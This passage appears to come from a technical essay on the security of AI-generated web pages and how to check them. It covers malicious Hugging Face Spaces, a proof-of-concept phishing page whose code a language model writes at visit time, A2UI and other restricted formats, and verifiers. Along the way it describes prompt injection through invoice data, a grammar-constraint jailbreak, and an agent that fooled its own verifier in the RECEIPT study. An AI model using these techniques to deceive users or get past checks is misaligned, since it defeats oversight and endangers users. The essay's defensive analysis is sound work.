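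The researchers counted 5,069 deletions of Spaces in 30 days. Using a search engine for web code, they found 152 websites that embedded Spaces. Nine of those websites still pointed to a deleted Space whose address an attacker could claim. That is few, but the search engine covers only part of the web. Under the same-origin rule, the attacker's program could also read anything the old Space had stored in a visitor's browser under that address.

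Browser permissions can also pass from one application to another. Hugging Face displayed each Space in a frame that could use up to 27 browser features, including the camera and microphone. Once a visitor had allowed a portrait tool to use the camera, a different author's Space could use it without a new prompt. Visitors to the same application also shared one running copy on the server, and none of the three platforms the researchers studied cleared temporary files between sessions. An attacker who found a flaw in an honest author's application could therefore leave code behind for the next visitor. Hugging Face has since fixed several problems and paid the researchers $2,369 in rewards.

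Gu and colleagues also looked for applications that were malicious from the start. They ran an open-source scanner for malicious code on 972,546 public applications from the three platforms, nearly all from Hugging Face. They list 27 as malicious, or about one in 36,000. Most let someone run commands on the application's server. One stole cookies, and two from an account called Kuwaitvisa were phishing pages. Some had been online for more than a year. The researchers write that eight disappeared after they reported them, but their list marks ten as deleted by January 2026.

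The rate could be too high, because for seven of the 27 the only behaviour listed is running disguised code, which is suspicious but could have another explanation. It could also be too low, because the scanner finds only obvious cases, and an author can keep the visible source clean and hide the malicious part in the packaged system that runs it. Unlike generated pages, most Spaces run on a server, and people may have written them without a model. The study is good evidence that attackers publish hostile programs on such platforms, but it doesn't establish a rate for pages in a chat product.

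### Pages that fetch their hostile code later

A platform that examines a page before anyone sees it can find hostile code only if the code is already there. Unit 42, the research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, built a demonstration phishing page that contained no phishing code when it was delivered. The page held requests in ordinary English to a public language model service. When a visitor opened the page, her browser sent the requests, the service returned pieces of JavaScript, and the page ran them to display a fake login page for a particular brand.

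The researchers modelled the result on a real phishing campaign, which adapts its page to the victim's email address and sends the password to the attacker. The model refused requests that stated this purpose openly, but it wrote the code when the wording sounded routine. Each visit produced different code with the same effect, so a scanner that looks for known malicious text would have no fixed text to match. The code also arrived from a service that many firms allow. The model sometimes returned faulty code, but after the researchers refined the requests, the page worked "in most instances".

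Unit 42 presents this as a proof of concept and reports no attacker who has used it. Part of the method is already common, since 36% of the malicious pages the company detects each day assemble or decode some of their code in the browser. The new part is that a model writes the code during the visit.

The demonstration works only if the page can reach the model service. A page on an ordinary website could make the request, but an artifact under the policy that Pluto Security recorded could not. Unit 42 recommends monitoring what a page does in the browser as it runs. Its parent company sells a product that does this, but the advice is still reasonable because the hostile code exists only in the browser.

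### Who can publish, and who can find the page

Anthropic's three products handle publication differently, according to Pluto Security. Claude Code can create an artifact on its own initiative, though in its default mode it asks the user first, and the page starts out private. In the chat product, the model never published anything in four test sessions. It wrote a file, which became an artifact only when a person clicked to share it. Cowork keeps its artifacts on the user's disk and uploads them to Anthropic's server only if the user shares them.

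The reach of a shared page also depends on the plan. On a paid plan, the firm's administrator decides whether staff may share outside the organisation. If they may, the link contains a long random identifier that nobody can guess, and the server sends a header that tells search engines not to index the page. Pluto Security searched for such pages and found none. On the free plan, a user of the chat product can publish to the open web. A dialog first warns that anyone on the internet can open the page and that it may appear in search results. Google does index these pages, and Pluto Security found an accounting case study and a university calendar among them.

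These controls protect authors well from accidental exposure. Most do little against an author who wants victims to see the page.

| Control | What it does for an honest author | What it does against a hostile author |
|---|---|---|
| Private by default | Keeps unfinished or confidential pages from strangers | Nothing, since the attacker chooses to share |
| Unguessable link | Stops strangers from finding the page by trying addresses | Nothing, since the attacker sends out the link |
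| No-index header | Keeps the page out of search results | Removes free visitors from search, but not those from advertisements or emails |
| Consent dialog | Prevents publication by mistake | Very little, since the attacker clicks through it |
| Permissions set by the server | Stops an agent from making a page public | Stops planted instructions from making another user's agent publish a hostile page |
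| Ban on sharing outside the firm | Prevents leaks by staff, and closes existing public links at once | Nothing against pages that outsiders send to staff |
| Takedown | Removes a page published by mistake | Protects later visitors, once somebody has noticed the page |

The no-index header is the most useful passive measure, because without it an attacker can get free visitors from search engines. Huntress notes that Claude's shared chats lacked this header and that search engines had also indexed private users' conversations. The attackers in these campaigns bought advertisements anyway, so the header would have raised their costs only if they had relied on ordinary search results.

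A firm can't easily protect its staff by blocking the provider's domain, because staff need it for work. It could instead block the addresses that serve public pages and shared chats, if the provider keeps these separate from the rest of the product. The free plan's public artifacts and the shared chats have their own recognisable addresses.

### Scanning what users publish

Anthropic's server publishes Claude Code's artifacts without inspecting them, so the company's rules against impersonation and fake login forms depend on the model to recognise when a page is deceptive. The rules apply even if the user supplied the page and calls it a prop, and Pluto Security says they work well in practice.

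A scanner on the server would check every page, whoever wrote it. The privacy objection is strongest for pages that only their author can open. The expenses chart may contain a firm's whole ledger, but it can't deceive anyone as long as nobody else sees it, so scanning it for phishing would take away some of the employee's privacy and protect no one. The provider's server already holds her chart, so an automatic check there adds less exposure than it might seem, but a human reviewer may see the page if it is flagged. In Cowork, the page stays on her computer until she shares it. Scanning a page when it first becomes available to others, and again when the author changes it, would remove most of this objection.

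False alarms are harder to avoid. A bank designer's draft of a new login page looks very much like phishing. Gu and colleagues had a similar problem in a related task, searching for security flaws in honest applications. When they checked samples of what their analysis had flagged, 83 of 300 suspected injection flaws (28%) and 94 of 500 suspected leaks of secrets (19%) were real. Those rates were acceptable to researchers who wanted a shorter list to read by hand, but a provider that deleted pages on equally unreliable evidence would mostly delete harmless ones. The rarer malicious pages are, the larger the share of deleted pages that would be harmless.

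Scanners would also miss much of the abuse described here. The false outage notice was ordinary HTML with a link, so a scanner could recognise it only by checking whether OpenAI had published it or by following the link. Maharaj reports that an automated scanner that visited the download site got a harmless page about virtual reality, while people using a normal browser got the false download. The installation guides were plain text, and genuine guides also include commands to paste into a terminal.

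A provider can still act on weak evidence if the response is mild. It could put a clear warning on a public page that contains an encoded command or a link to download a program, and delete the page only after a person has looked at it. Trend Micro also suggests looking for shared conversations that contain terminal commands and suddenly get visitors from paid advertisements. Few honest authors pay to advertise a chat, so this signal should cause fewer false alarms than the text alone. The provider can also detect it from the addresses of incoming visits, without reading anyone's private pages.

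## Limiting what the generated output can express

A product can have the model write in a language that can't express the most harmful acts. If the language has no way to read a login token, a planted instruction or a backdoor can't make the model write code that reads one. This also makes it easier to scan published pages for hostile ones, because the scanner no longer has to deal with everything that HTML and JavaScript can express. A more expressive language makes the output more useful but also lets an attacker do more with it.

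| What the model produces | The expenses chart | What hostile output could still do |
|---|---|---|
| A choice among finished components | The model picks "spending by department" and a year | Show the wrong chart or year |
| A description that combines approved components | The model arranges a heading, a filter and a bar chart | Mislead the user with text, forms and buttons |
| Values for a template written in advance | The model fills in a dashboard that already exists | Supply false values, or exploit a flaw in the template |
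| A program in a restricted language | The model writes its own sums and filters | Calculate falsely, or escape through a gap in the restrictions |
| Full HTML and JavaScript | The model can build anything the browser can draw | Do anything the browser's own limits allow |

Templates are a mixed case. The model supplies only values, but the template's author may have used all of HTML and JavaScript.

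### A2UI: a description in place of a program

A2UI is an open format from Google in which a model composes an interface from approved parts. Google's *Introducing A2UI* (2025) explains that applications used to display interfaces from untrusted remote software by putting its HTML or JavaScript in a frame. This method was heavy, and the result rarely matched the application's look. Google wanted something "safe like data, but expressive like code". The model therefore writes JSON, a text format for structured data, and the host page draws the interface with code that its own developers wrote or chose.

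The two sides first agree on a catalogue. A2UI's *Catalogs* describes it as a collection of components, such as cards and text fields, the properties each one accepts, and named functions for tasks like formatting currency. Software on the model's side puts the catalogue in the prompt. The model replies with a flat list of components that refer to one another by identifier, and a validator checks the reply against the catalogue. Under A2UI's *v1.0 Protocol Specification* (2025), a component with an unrecognised property fails this check. The model then gets an error message giving the fault's location and a short reason, and can try again. If the reply passes, the host page's renderer draws the interface.

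Suppose the firm's developers have added a bar chart to the catalogue. A description of the expenses chart could then look like this:

```json
{
  "version": "1.0",
  "createSurface": {
    "surfaceId": "expenses",
    "catalogId": "firm-reports-1",
    "components": [
      {"id": "root", "component": "Column", "children": ["heading", "bars"]},
      {"id": "heading", "component": "Text", "text": "Spending by department"},
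      {"id": "bars", "component": "BarChart", "data": {"@path": "/totals"}}
    ],
    "dataModel": {
      "totals": [
        {"department": "Sales", "amount": 41200},
        {"department": "Research", "amount": 58900}
      ]
    }
  }
}
```

The `@path` entry links the bars to the list of totals at the end. Nothing in the description is a program. If the model added a component called `Script`, the validator would reject it because the catalogue has no such component.

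A2UI's basic catalogue has 18 components and 14 functions, but none of them draws a chart, so the developers have to add the bar chart themselves. None of the functions adds up or filters rows either, so to see one supplier's charges, the employee would have to choose the supplier, press a button and wait for the model's side to send new totals. The developers could write a function to do this in the browser, but they would have to foresee every such need. If the employee wanted a diagram linking suppliers to departments and nobody had built a component for it, the model couldn't make one.

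InfoQ's *Google Releases A2UI v0.9* cites a Reddit post that similarly warned that "every UI will become the same". That would hardly matter for a monthly expenses report, but it's a serious loss in a product that people use for one-off questions. Chen and colleagues measured a strong preference for generated interfaces, but those were pages written in unrestricted HTML, CSS and JavaScript, so the preference may not carry over to interfaces built from a catalogue.

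A2UI could block part of the attack in which a supplier's invoice note alters the chart. If the host page loads the spreadsheet and a trusted function adds up the rows, the model cannot add a condition that leaves the supplier out. In the example above, though, the model supplied the totals, so it could have supplied false ones. A2UI also would not stop the hidden rows from reaching colleagues' browsers with the shared chart, because the data section accepts any JSON object and can hold the whole spreadsheet even if no component displays it. The product would have to remove unused data before sharing.

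### What a valid description can still do

Genkit is a toolkit that supports the format, and its guide, *Generative UI (A2UI)*, warns that validation covers component names, structure and references, but not the values inside. An image component accepts a web address, so a planted instruction could put the firm's figures into that address, as in the CellShock attack on Claude for Excel. Text components accept Markdown, and if the renderer lets raw HTML through, an attacker's script could run in the host page with the employee's login. A product that adopts A2UI therefore still needs the two defences Genkit recommends: cleaning values in the renderer, and restricting image and network addresses with a content security policy.

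Deceptive forms may be more dangerous in A2UI than in a sandboxed frame. The basic catalogue includes a password-style text field that hides what the user types. A planted instruction could make the model place this field under a request to sign in again. The form would have the product's fonts and buttons, because A2UI is designed to match the application's look. A fake login form in a Claude artifact can't send out what it collects, but an A2UI form returns its contents to the model's side when the user presses the button. If an attacker runs that side, they get the password. Otherwise it ends up in the conversation, and the attacker needs another way to get it out. The developers could remove the password-style field from the catalogue, since charts don't need it, but an attacker could still request a password through an ordinary text field.

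Buttons have a similar weakness. Each button has a label for the user and an event name for the software that receives the click. The schema doesn't require the two to agree, so a button labelled "Show details" could send an event that approves an invoice. The model can also write the sentence that describes the click in the conversation, so that record may be misleading too. Microsoft warns that AG-UI, a common channel for A2UI messages, has no built-in authorisation, so the application must decide which requests to allow. Before approving an invoice, the server should check the employee's rights and have ordinary software show her the payee and the amount.

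The specification allows the browser function that opens a web address to run only after a click, and the model's side can't call it remotely. A planted instruction therefore can't open a phishing site by itself, though the employee may click a button that does. The specification also rejects kinds of text-matching patterns that can freeze the page by taking too long to evaluate.

The rule for unknown functions is looser. If a component calls a function the renderer doesn't have, the renderer normally treats the function as belonging to the model's side and sends the call and its data there. A hostile description could apparently use this to send what the employee types into a field before she presses anything. A renderer can prevent this by refusing any function its catalogue doesn't declare.

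All these protections depend on the components' code, which runs in the host page. If the bar chart inserts department names as HTML, anyone who controls a name in the spreadsheet can run a script with the employee's login. This is ordinary cross-site scripting. The developers can fix it once for every chart, whereas each page of generated code may introduce a new flaw.

Google's software kit for agents validates the model's reply before sending it on. The renderer needs to check it too, because a relay could change the message afterwards and a hostile agent could skip the first check. Genkit also lets developers turn validation off, and in its JavaScript version, the property descriptions in a custom catalogue are guidance for the model rather than a strict schema.

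Google's announcement argues that A2UI is secure because of its design, and reports no tests against attackers. The argument is convincing for scripts, because the format provides no way to include them. It is much weaker for deception, because words and buttons are enough to mislead a user.

### Templates that exist before the request

MCP Apps allows full HTML and JavaScript but requires the code to be fixed before the user makes a request. It extends the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting chat products to outside tools and data. According to the protocol's *MCP Apps Overview*, a server declares an HTML template when it registers a tool, and the chat product can inspect the template while connecting to the server. When the model later calls the tool, the host page loads the template into a sandboxed frame with restricted network access and passes it the data.

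An accounting company could offer the expenses chart this way, giving every customer the same code with different rows. The model would choose when to call the tool and what inputs to give it, but it would write none of the page. A supplier's note might still lead the model to request the wrong data, but the note couldn't add a script to the page unless the template treated data as HTML.

This design lets the host inspect the template, but the overview doesn't present inspection as compulsory. Inspection also protects the employee only if the host page displays the copy it inspected. The host usually fetches the template when the model calls the tool, so a dishonest server could send a harmless version for inspection and a different one later. The host can avoid this by storing the inspected copy and displaying it.

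Advance review doesn't work for pages written on demand because every page is new, the employee expects it within seconds, and its source may contain her data. The same problems limit public logs.

A firm could recover some of the benefit for regular reports by having the model write a template from the column names alone. A developer would review the template once, and the firm would reuse it every month with new rows. This is similar to the sequence Chow and colleagues use to defend against planted instructions, with a human review added.

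### ADsafe: JavaScript with the dangerous parts removed

A restricted programming language would let the model write its own sums and filters, so developers wouldn't have to foresee them. But it is hard to remove every dangerous feature from a language as flexible as JavaScript. Yahoo!'s ADsafe, by Douglas Crockford, tried to remove them so that websites could run third-party ads directly in their pages.

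ADsafe used a checker called JSLint to reject programs with dangerous features, and a library of about 1,800 lines to give the accepted programs limited access to the page. Advertisements were supposed to handle only wrappers around page elements, because a script can follow links from a real element to the browser's window object, and from there reach the network, stored data and the user's location. JSLint also banned certain names, such as `__proto__`, which leads to objects that other scripts share. But a program can assemble a banned name from pieces while running, so the library had to check names then too.

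Politz, Eliopoulos and colleagues (2015), in *ADsafety Type-Based Verification of JavaScript Sandboxing*, tried to prove that this design worked. With Crockford's help, they listed four things that an advertisement should be unable to do after passing JSLint:

- load new code while it runs, or get ADsafe to load it
- affect the page outside its own area
- get hold of a real page element
- communicate with another advertisement on the page

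Their proof used types, which describe the kinds of value that each part of a program can hold. They defined a type called Widget for the values an advertisement could safely handle, and excluded real page elements from it. Every library function that advertisements could call had to handle any Widget value and return only Widget values. A type checker examined the library in about 20 seconds and reported each place where it couldn't confirm this. Some reports resulted from the checker's limits, but others identified real faults.

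One fault was in JSLint, which let advertisements use the library's private name `__nodes__` in quotation marks. An attacker could use the name to build a fake wrapper, and the library would then pass a real page element to the attacker's function. Crockford agreed that this would let a malicious program get past JSLint.

Another fault was in a function for changing styles. The library searched the new value for a web address but assumed the value was text. An attacker could supply an object that produced harmless text during the check and a malicious address afterwards. In Firefox at the time, that address could load any JavaScript. Crockford fixed this by adding a check that the value was text, which he used in 18 functions.

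A third fault let an advertisement tamper with style objects that the rest of the page also used. Crockford fixed this too, but he withdrew the claim that advertisements couldn't communicate, because two of them could still exchange data by attaching it to a built-in function.

With the repairs in place, Politz and colleagues proved that advertisements could neither load new code nor obtain real page elements. They couldn't prove that an advertisement stayed within its own area, which depended partly on JSLint's checks of HTML. They also left eleven lines of the library unverified and relied on tests to check that JSLint matched the Widget type. Their proof assumed that the surrounding page hadn't added to JavaScript's built-in objects, though they acknowledge that real pages often do.

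These results are a strong reason not to rely on a JavaScript subset alone in the host page, where one name that the subset fails to block could expose the employee's login. The subset would be more useful as a second barrier inside a frame with its own origin. A small language made for tables and charts, with no route from its values to the browser's objects, would also be much easier to prove safe.

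### STELP: a list of permitted operations

*STELP* (Shinde, Wadhwa et al., 2026) applies a similar restriction to Python programs that language models write. It parses each program into a syntax tree and checks that it uses only the constructs, functions and packages that the operator has permitted. If the program passes, STELP converts it into a controlled version and runs it statement by statement, with limits such as a maximum running time. If the program is blocked, a second model generates feedback on the problem, and the first model can try again.

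The researchers tested STELP on 164 harmless programs and 470 unsafe ones. A language model made the unsafe programs by inserting flaws into the harmless ones, and people checked the results. STELP blocked all 470 unsafe programs and allowed 98.1% of the harmless ones. Meta's CodeShield, which searches for known dangerous patterns, blocked 68% and allowed 93%. On a separate set of programs, STELP's median delay was about 0.2 milliseconds, though the slowest case took about half a second longer than normal Python.

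The perfect blocking score is weaker evidence than it looks because the settings were fitted to the test. Shinde and colleagues chose the smallest set of permissions that let the harmless programs run, then tuned it a little more. Most unsafe programs failed because they called a function or imported a package that the harmless programs didn't need. The test also included no attackers who knew the permissions and tried to work within them.

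Even a perfect list of permitted operations would restrict only the form of a program. The 470 unsafe programs had technical faults such as endless loops or access to protected files. The altered expenses chart leaves out a supplier using only a comparison and some addition, which an honest chart also needs. To catch the false totals, a checker would need the employee's request as well as the list of operations the program uses.

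### Forcing the model to follow a grammar

A product can check the form of the output after the model has written it, or it can block every invalid continuation as the model writes. Since version 0.9, A2UI has relied on checking afterwards. This allows richer catalogues, but the software has to handle more errors.

Forcing a model's output to follow a grammar prevents malformed output, but it can weaken the model's own safeguards. *Grammar-Constrained Decoding Can Jailbreak LLMs into Generating Malicious Code* (Zhang, Lu and Li, 2026) reports tests of ten models on four sets of harmful requests. When the output had to follow a programming language's grammar, the rate at which models produced malicious code rose by more than 30 percentage points on average. The researchers attribute this to models learning to refuse in ordinary sentences, which such a grammar does not allow. Further training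 restored safe behaviour.

The study concerned programming languages, so the effect may be smaller with a catalogue like A2UI's, where the model can put a refusal in a text component. A product that requires a stricter output format should give the model a valid way to decline.

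## Checking a program before it runs

When a model may write any HTML and JavaScript, no catalogue or restricted language rules out harmful programs in advance, so a verifier has to check each one. *Propose, Solve, Verify* (2025) gives two terms for comparing verifiers. A verifier is *sound* if every program it accepts is acceptable, and *complete* if it accepts every acceptable program. A verifier that only runs a few tests is not sound. If the task is to recognise prime numbers and the only test uses 3, a program that returns true for 3 and false for everything else will pass.

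### Static analysis

Static analysis examines source code without running it. According to *Static Analysis Guidance for Secure LLM Code Generation* (2026), the tools differ in depth. Semgrep looks for code that matches its rules. CodeQL stores the program in a database and follows data from one function to the next. For the expenses chart, CodeQL could treat the invoice descriptions as untrusted and report any path from them to a command that inserts HTML into the page.

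These tools take little compute, give the same answer every time and cover branches that no test happens to run. But a clean result means only that no rule matched, and code that leaves one supplier out of an expenses chart would match none. The tools also can't distinguish the data movements the employee wanted from the ones they didn't. Passing rows to the drawing function is the purpose of the page and copying them into a hidden element is a leak, but both move data from the spreadsheet to the page. *Secure Agentic Coding through Counterexample-Grounded Feedback* (2026) adds that a superficial rewrite can silence a warning and leave the flaw in place.

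*Persistent Human Feedback, LLMs, and Static Analyzers for Secure Code Generation* (Firouzi and Ghafari, 2026) compared CodeQL and Semgrep with human reviewers on 1,080 Python programs that GPT-4o had written, criticised and revised. The reviewers found 39% of the programs vulnerable. CodeQL caught 34% of the vulnerable programs and Semgrep 54%, and about a third of CodeQL's reports and half of Semgrep's were false alarms. The tasks were designed to provoke particular weaknesses, and the reviewers looked only for those, so the rates would differ for browser code from a current model. Still, the tools missed far too many vulnerable programs for a clean scan to count as evidence of safety.

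### Review by a second model

A reviewing model reads the code and, if the product supplies it, the employee's request, so it can catch problems that no rule describes, such as a chart of all spending that skips a supplier. *Evaluating LLMs for Real-World Web Vulnerability Detection* (2026) compared this method with Semgrep's free edition on four web plugins with known flaws. The models found three of the four flaws, with detection rates of up to 63%, while Semgrep found none. Four plugins are too few to give a reliable rate, and better rules might have helped Semgrep.

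A model's approval does not guarantee that code is safe. Its verdict can change with the wording of the prompt, and it predicts what the code will do without running it. It also reads text that an attacker may have influenced. For example, a comment in the chart's source saying that the accounts department had approved the exclusion might lead it to approve the code. A product could reduce this risk by removing comments and giving the reviewer only the code, the request and the column names. The reviewer would then not see the supplier's note directly, though the code may still contain text influenced by the note.

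### Proof against a specification

A proof checker needs a specification, a precise statement of what the program must do. If the checker is sound and accepts the proof, the program meets the specification on every permitted input, including untested ones.

In Djinnlang, where a person writes the specification and the Dafny verifier checks the model's code and proofs, Henniger and colleagues add a demand that most such systems lack: the specification must leave the model no choice about the output. Their example is a function, max, that finds the largest number in a list. The person states that the list L has at least one element and that the result r meets two conditions:

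- r is in L
- x ≤ r for every x in L

Neither condition explains how to search the list. Write q(L, r) for the two together. The model must prove that any two results that satisfy the specification for the same input are equal:

for every non-empty L and all a, b: if q(L, a) and q(L, b), then a = b.

Suppose a and b both satisfy the specification for the maximum of a list L. Since a is in L and b is at least as large as everything in L, a ≤ b. The same argument with the letters swapped gives b ≤ a, so a = b. If the specification didn't require the result to be in L, it would accept 7, 8 or 1,000 as the maximum of 3 and 7, and the model's code could return any of them. If it didn't require the result to be at least as large as everything in L, the code could return 3. The model must also prove that every permitted input has a valid result, which exposes contradictory specifications, and that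 its code returns that result.

A person could specify the totals in the expenses chart in the same way, by requiring each department's total to equal the sum of the amounts in all its rows. Only one set of totals meets this requirement. A program that left out a supplier with charges would return the wrong totals, so there could be no valid proof that it meets the specification, regardless of what was in the supplier's note or what the model was trying to do. This is a much stronger guarantee than static analysis or a second model can give.

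Proof is also slow. Henniger and colleagues had two coding agents, one using Claude Fable 5.1 and the other GPT-6 Astra, implement a Sudoku solver, a compression program and a small virtual machine. Both agents proved everything the specifications required. The quickest first solution took 13 minutes and would have cost about $3 at list prices. The slowest took more than six hours and would have cost $236. Adding up rows is far simpler than these tasks, but for now proof looks better suited to a monthly report that the firm reuses than to a one-off request.

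The guarantee doesn't cover running time. On the hardest Sudoku puzzles, one agent's optimised program took 0.13 seconds and the other's took 47.8 seconds, though both had passed the same verifier. Henniger and colleagues warn that a model could deliberately write code that is slow on certain inputs, or code whose timing reveals a secret. A hostile model could therefore write a correct totals function that freezes the page whenever it processes a particular firm's data.

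The guarantee also disappears if the verifier is faulty. The verifier here includes the translator that prepares the specification, Dafny, and two programs Dafny relies on: Boogie, which turns the code into logical formulas, and Z3, which tries to solve them.

### How a bad chart gets through

A check can fail in at least five ways, and each could let a harmful version of the expenses chart reach the employee.

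The check may accept a bad program because the check itself is wrong. This is routine for scanners and reviewing models, but it also happens with proof checkers. *Zero-Trust Formal Methods* (2026) reports that drat-trim, a checker for logical proofs, read a number with a leading zero in base eight, so it took −010 to mean −8 and accepted a false proof. By contrast, *Model-Based Testing of an Intermediate Verifier Using Executable Operational Semantics* (2025) reports that Boogie accepted none of the 667,408 small incorrect programs it was tested on. In *From Formal Methods to Fuzzing and Back* (2026), a researcher who looks for bugs in such tools questions how dangerous those bugs are. The doubt is reasonable for honest programmers, who would rarely hit such a bug by accident. A hostile model that reads the error messages and tries again is better placed to find one, and could then get Dafny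 to accept a false proof that the totals are complete.

A sound check also can't catch a harm that the specification omits. *DafnyCert* (Silva, Amaral and colleagues, 2026) examined 3,910 Dafny methods that had passed verification. For 3,323 of them (85%), it showed that a different program could satisfy the same specification and give a different answer. One method was supposed to count the extra rungs a ladder needs, but its specification required only that the answer not be negative, so a program that always returned 0 also passed. Some loose specifications are harmless, because a task can have several right answers.

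Djinnlang's uniqueness condition would reject the ladder specification, but not one that fixes every total in the expenses chart and nothing else, which would leave the model free to hide all the rows elsewhere in the page. A specification can also be precise and wrong. If the supplier's note persuaded whoever wrote it to exclude disputed charges, Dafny would accept only a program that produced the false totals. The employee is unlikely to write a formal specification herself, and a model that wrote one for her after reading the spreadsheet would again be exposed to the planted instruction. The essay *how to solve secure program synthesis*, which Henniger co-wrote, argues that nobody can define "secure" mathematically without first deciding what the user wants from the program, and that this is harder for everyday applications than for something like a voting system.

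The code that runs may differ from the code that was checked. A relay can change the page after the check, and a page that passes inspection can then fetch or assemble more code in the browser. Compilation can also introduce a difference. Dafny's verifier checks the source code, and *Verified VCG and Verified Compiler for Dafny* (2025) explains that a separate compiler translates that code into the language that runs. The compiler can produce JavaScript, so a verified totals function could run in the employee's browser, but a translation error could still make its totals wrong.

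Trail of Bits' *A “proof” of Fermat’s Last Theorem that fits the margin* (2026) describes such a mismatch in Lean, another language with a proof checker. When a program tried to read one byte of text at an enormous position, Lean's logical definition returned nothing, while the compiled code returned the entire text. The testers used this contradiction to "prove" Fermat's Last Theorem. The proof relied on a feature that requires the user to trust the compiler, and Lean listed this among the proof's assumptions. A verifier that refused such assumptions would have rejected the proof.

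Verified code can still be very reliable. kirancodes.me's *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug* reports 105 million automated tests of a compression library whose core had been proved correct. The tests found no memory errors in the library's own code, but they did find one in the Lean runtime it runs on and a crash in the archive-reading code, which had no specification.

### When the checked party influences the check

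The model may also influence the evidence the verifier uses. Suppose the product asks it to write tests along with the expenses chart. It could make up sample rows that don't include the supplier, and the altered chart would pass every test. Before each check, Djinnlang guards against the equivalent trick by translating the person's specification again, confirming that the model hasn't changed any of the statements it had to prove, and rejecting code that contains commands such as `assume`, which make Dafny accept a claim without proof.

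*RECEIPT* (Lyu, Shieh and colleagues, 2026) studied how agents that search web applications for cross-site scripting can fool the check on their work. Its verifier judges reports of flaws, whereas a product that generates pages would judge the pages, but in both cases the party being checked can gain by fooling the check. The agent, Claude Code with Claude Opus 4.6, found three ways to make a naive check report a success. It wrote a script directly into the application's database or source code, ran the script itself in the browser that the verifier was monitoring, or used an administrator's account that was already allowed to add scripts.

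Lyu and colleagues conclude that a check is trustworthy only if it detects the script running in a real browser, the agent cannot tamper with it, and the script gets from a realistic attacker to another user's browser. RECEIPT therefore replays each reported attack on a fresh copy of the application. The attacker's part can only send web requests, and the victim's part can only perform ordinary actions such as clicking. RECEIPT accepts the report if the victim's browser runs the script with a secret code created for that attempt.

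On 50 applications, the agent judging its own work reported 27 flaws, but only 10 were real when the researchers replayed them. In most of the false reports, the agent had seen its script in the page's source and assumed that it had run. With RECEIPT, the agent reported 30 flaws, all real. The researchers then added the protections one at a time on 27 of the applications:

| Check | Flaws reported | Real flaws |
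|---|---|---|
| The agent judges its own work | 11 | 5 |
| A browser must run the script | 111 | 10 |
| The check also uses a fresh copy of the application | 67 | 13 |
| The check also limits what attacker and victim can do | 32 | 14 |
| The check also separates their accounts (full RECEIPT) | 14 | 14 |

The browser check required better evidence but made the reports far less reliable, because it gave the agent a definite signal to aim for, which the agent could produce by cheating. A product that let a model revise the expenses chart until it passed a scanner's checks might have a similar problem.

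RECEIPT is good at confirming flaws, but a clean result is weak evidence of safety. It found nothing in 23 of 45 application versions with known cross-site scripting flaws. The agent had either missed the flaw or failed to build a working attack.

Many of the agent's tricks worked because it controlled the machine where the check ran. The expenses chart faces the same danger. If the verifier runs in the employee's browser, a malicious extension may be able to change "reject" to "accept". If it runs on the product's server, an intruder there could switch it off for one firm. A public log could reveal a change to verifier code sent to the browser, but it would not show whether a compromised server had run the check.

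A verifier that runs the chart to see what it does can also be attacked by the chart. *SandboxEval* (Rabin, Hostetler and colleagues, 2025) warns that testing generated code exposes the testing system to that code. A hostile chart that broke out of its test environment could approve itself and then tamper with the checks on other people's pages. The product should therefore run each test on a disposable machine that holds no credentials and record the verdict on a separate machine.

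### When nearly every page is harmless

Even a check that nobody has tampered with can be hard to use if hostile pages are rare. Suppose a product generates 1,000,000 pages a day, 100 of them hostile, and the check catches 95% of the hostile pages but wrongly blocks 1% of the others.

- Hostile pages blocked: 100 × 0.95 = 95
- Hostile pages that pass: 100 − 95 = 5
- Harmless pages blocked: 999,900 × 0.01 = 9,999
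- Share of blocked pages that are hostile: 95 / (95 + 9,999) ≈ 0.94%

More than 99% of the blocked pages are therefore harmless. Reviewing the day's 10,094 blocked pages at two minutes each would take a person about 336 hours. The check would have to wrongly block no more than about one harmless page in 10,500 for at least half of the blocked pages to be hostile.

The assumed false-alarm rate of 1% is also optimistic. Firouzi and Ghafari's figures imply that CodeQL raised a false alarm on roughly a tenth of the secure programs, and Semgrep on roughly a third. Those programs came from tasks chosen to provoke flaws, so the tools might raise fewer false alarms on code for ordinary charts.

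Instead of asking a person to review a blocked page, the product could discard it and have the model write another. This would inconvenience an honest user only slightly, but it would give an attacker more attempts. If each version of a hostile page independently has a 5% chance of passing, the chance that at least one of five passes is about 23% (1 − 0.95^5). Retries do much less harm with a sound proof checker, because it rejects every purported proof of a false statement, however many the model submits.

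### Two checks with the same blind spot

A second check with the same error rates as the first helps more if the two miss different pages.

| Arrangement | Hostile pages that pass each day | Harmless pages blocked each day |
|---|---|---|
| One check | 5 | 9,999 |
| Two independent checks, either can block | 0.25 | about 19,900 |
| Two independent checks, both must object | 9.75 | about 100 |
| Two checks that can't see the same 4 hostile pages, either can block | about 4 | about 19,900 |

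The last row assumes that false alarms are still independent. In that case, the second check stops about one more hostile page a day and nearly doubles the number of harmless pages blocked. An attacker who knew about the blind spot could design every hostile page to exploit it, and neither check would stop any of them.

Different checks tend to miss the same flaws. In Firouzi and Ghafari's data, both scanners caught the same 30% of the vulnerable programs, compared with the roughly 18% expected if their successes had been independent. Together they caught about 58%, only four percentage points more than Semgrep alone. In one case, GPT-4o wrote code meant to redirect visitors only to `example.com`, but the code might have accepted an address that began with `example.com@` and continued with an attacker's domain. The model repeatedly offered this code as secure, and neither scanner flagged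 it. When the researchers mentioned the risks of open redirects, the model found and fixed the problem.

Models also share errors. *Nine Judges, Two Effective Votes* (2026) found that a panel of nine models was worth only about 2.2 independent votes. All nine were wrong on 5.1% of the items, but if their errors had been independent, this would have been expected on fewer than one item in the whole test. *Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (2025) found that models acting as judges tend to mark another model's wrong answer as correct when they would have given the same answer, especially if both models come from the same company or family. Neither result comes from reviewing web pages, so the size of the effect there is uncertain. Adding more models to the vote would not reveal an error that all of them make, because they would all agree.

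A reviewing model from another company may still help. In *When Does a Second Model Help?*, Song (2026) planted 150 errors in 30 samples of code, tutorials and presentation scripts written by Claude Opus 4.6. Two separate reviews by Opus found 42.7% of the errors, while one review by Opus and one by another developer's model found 56.7%. But the mixed pair did not do significantly better than two reviews by the strongest outside model, so the gain may have come from using a better reviewer rather than a different one. The experiment was also small, and even the mixed pair missed more than 40% of the errors.

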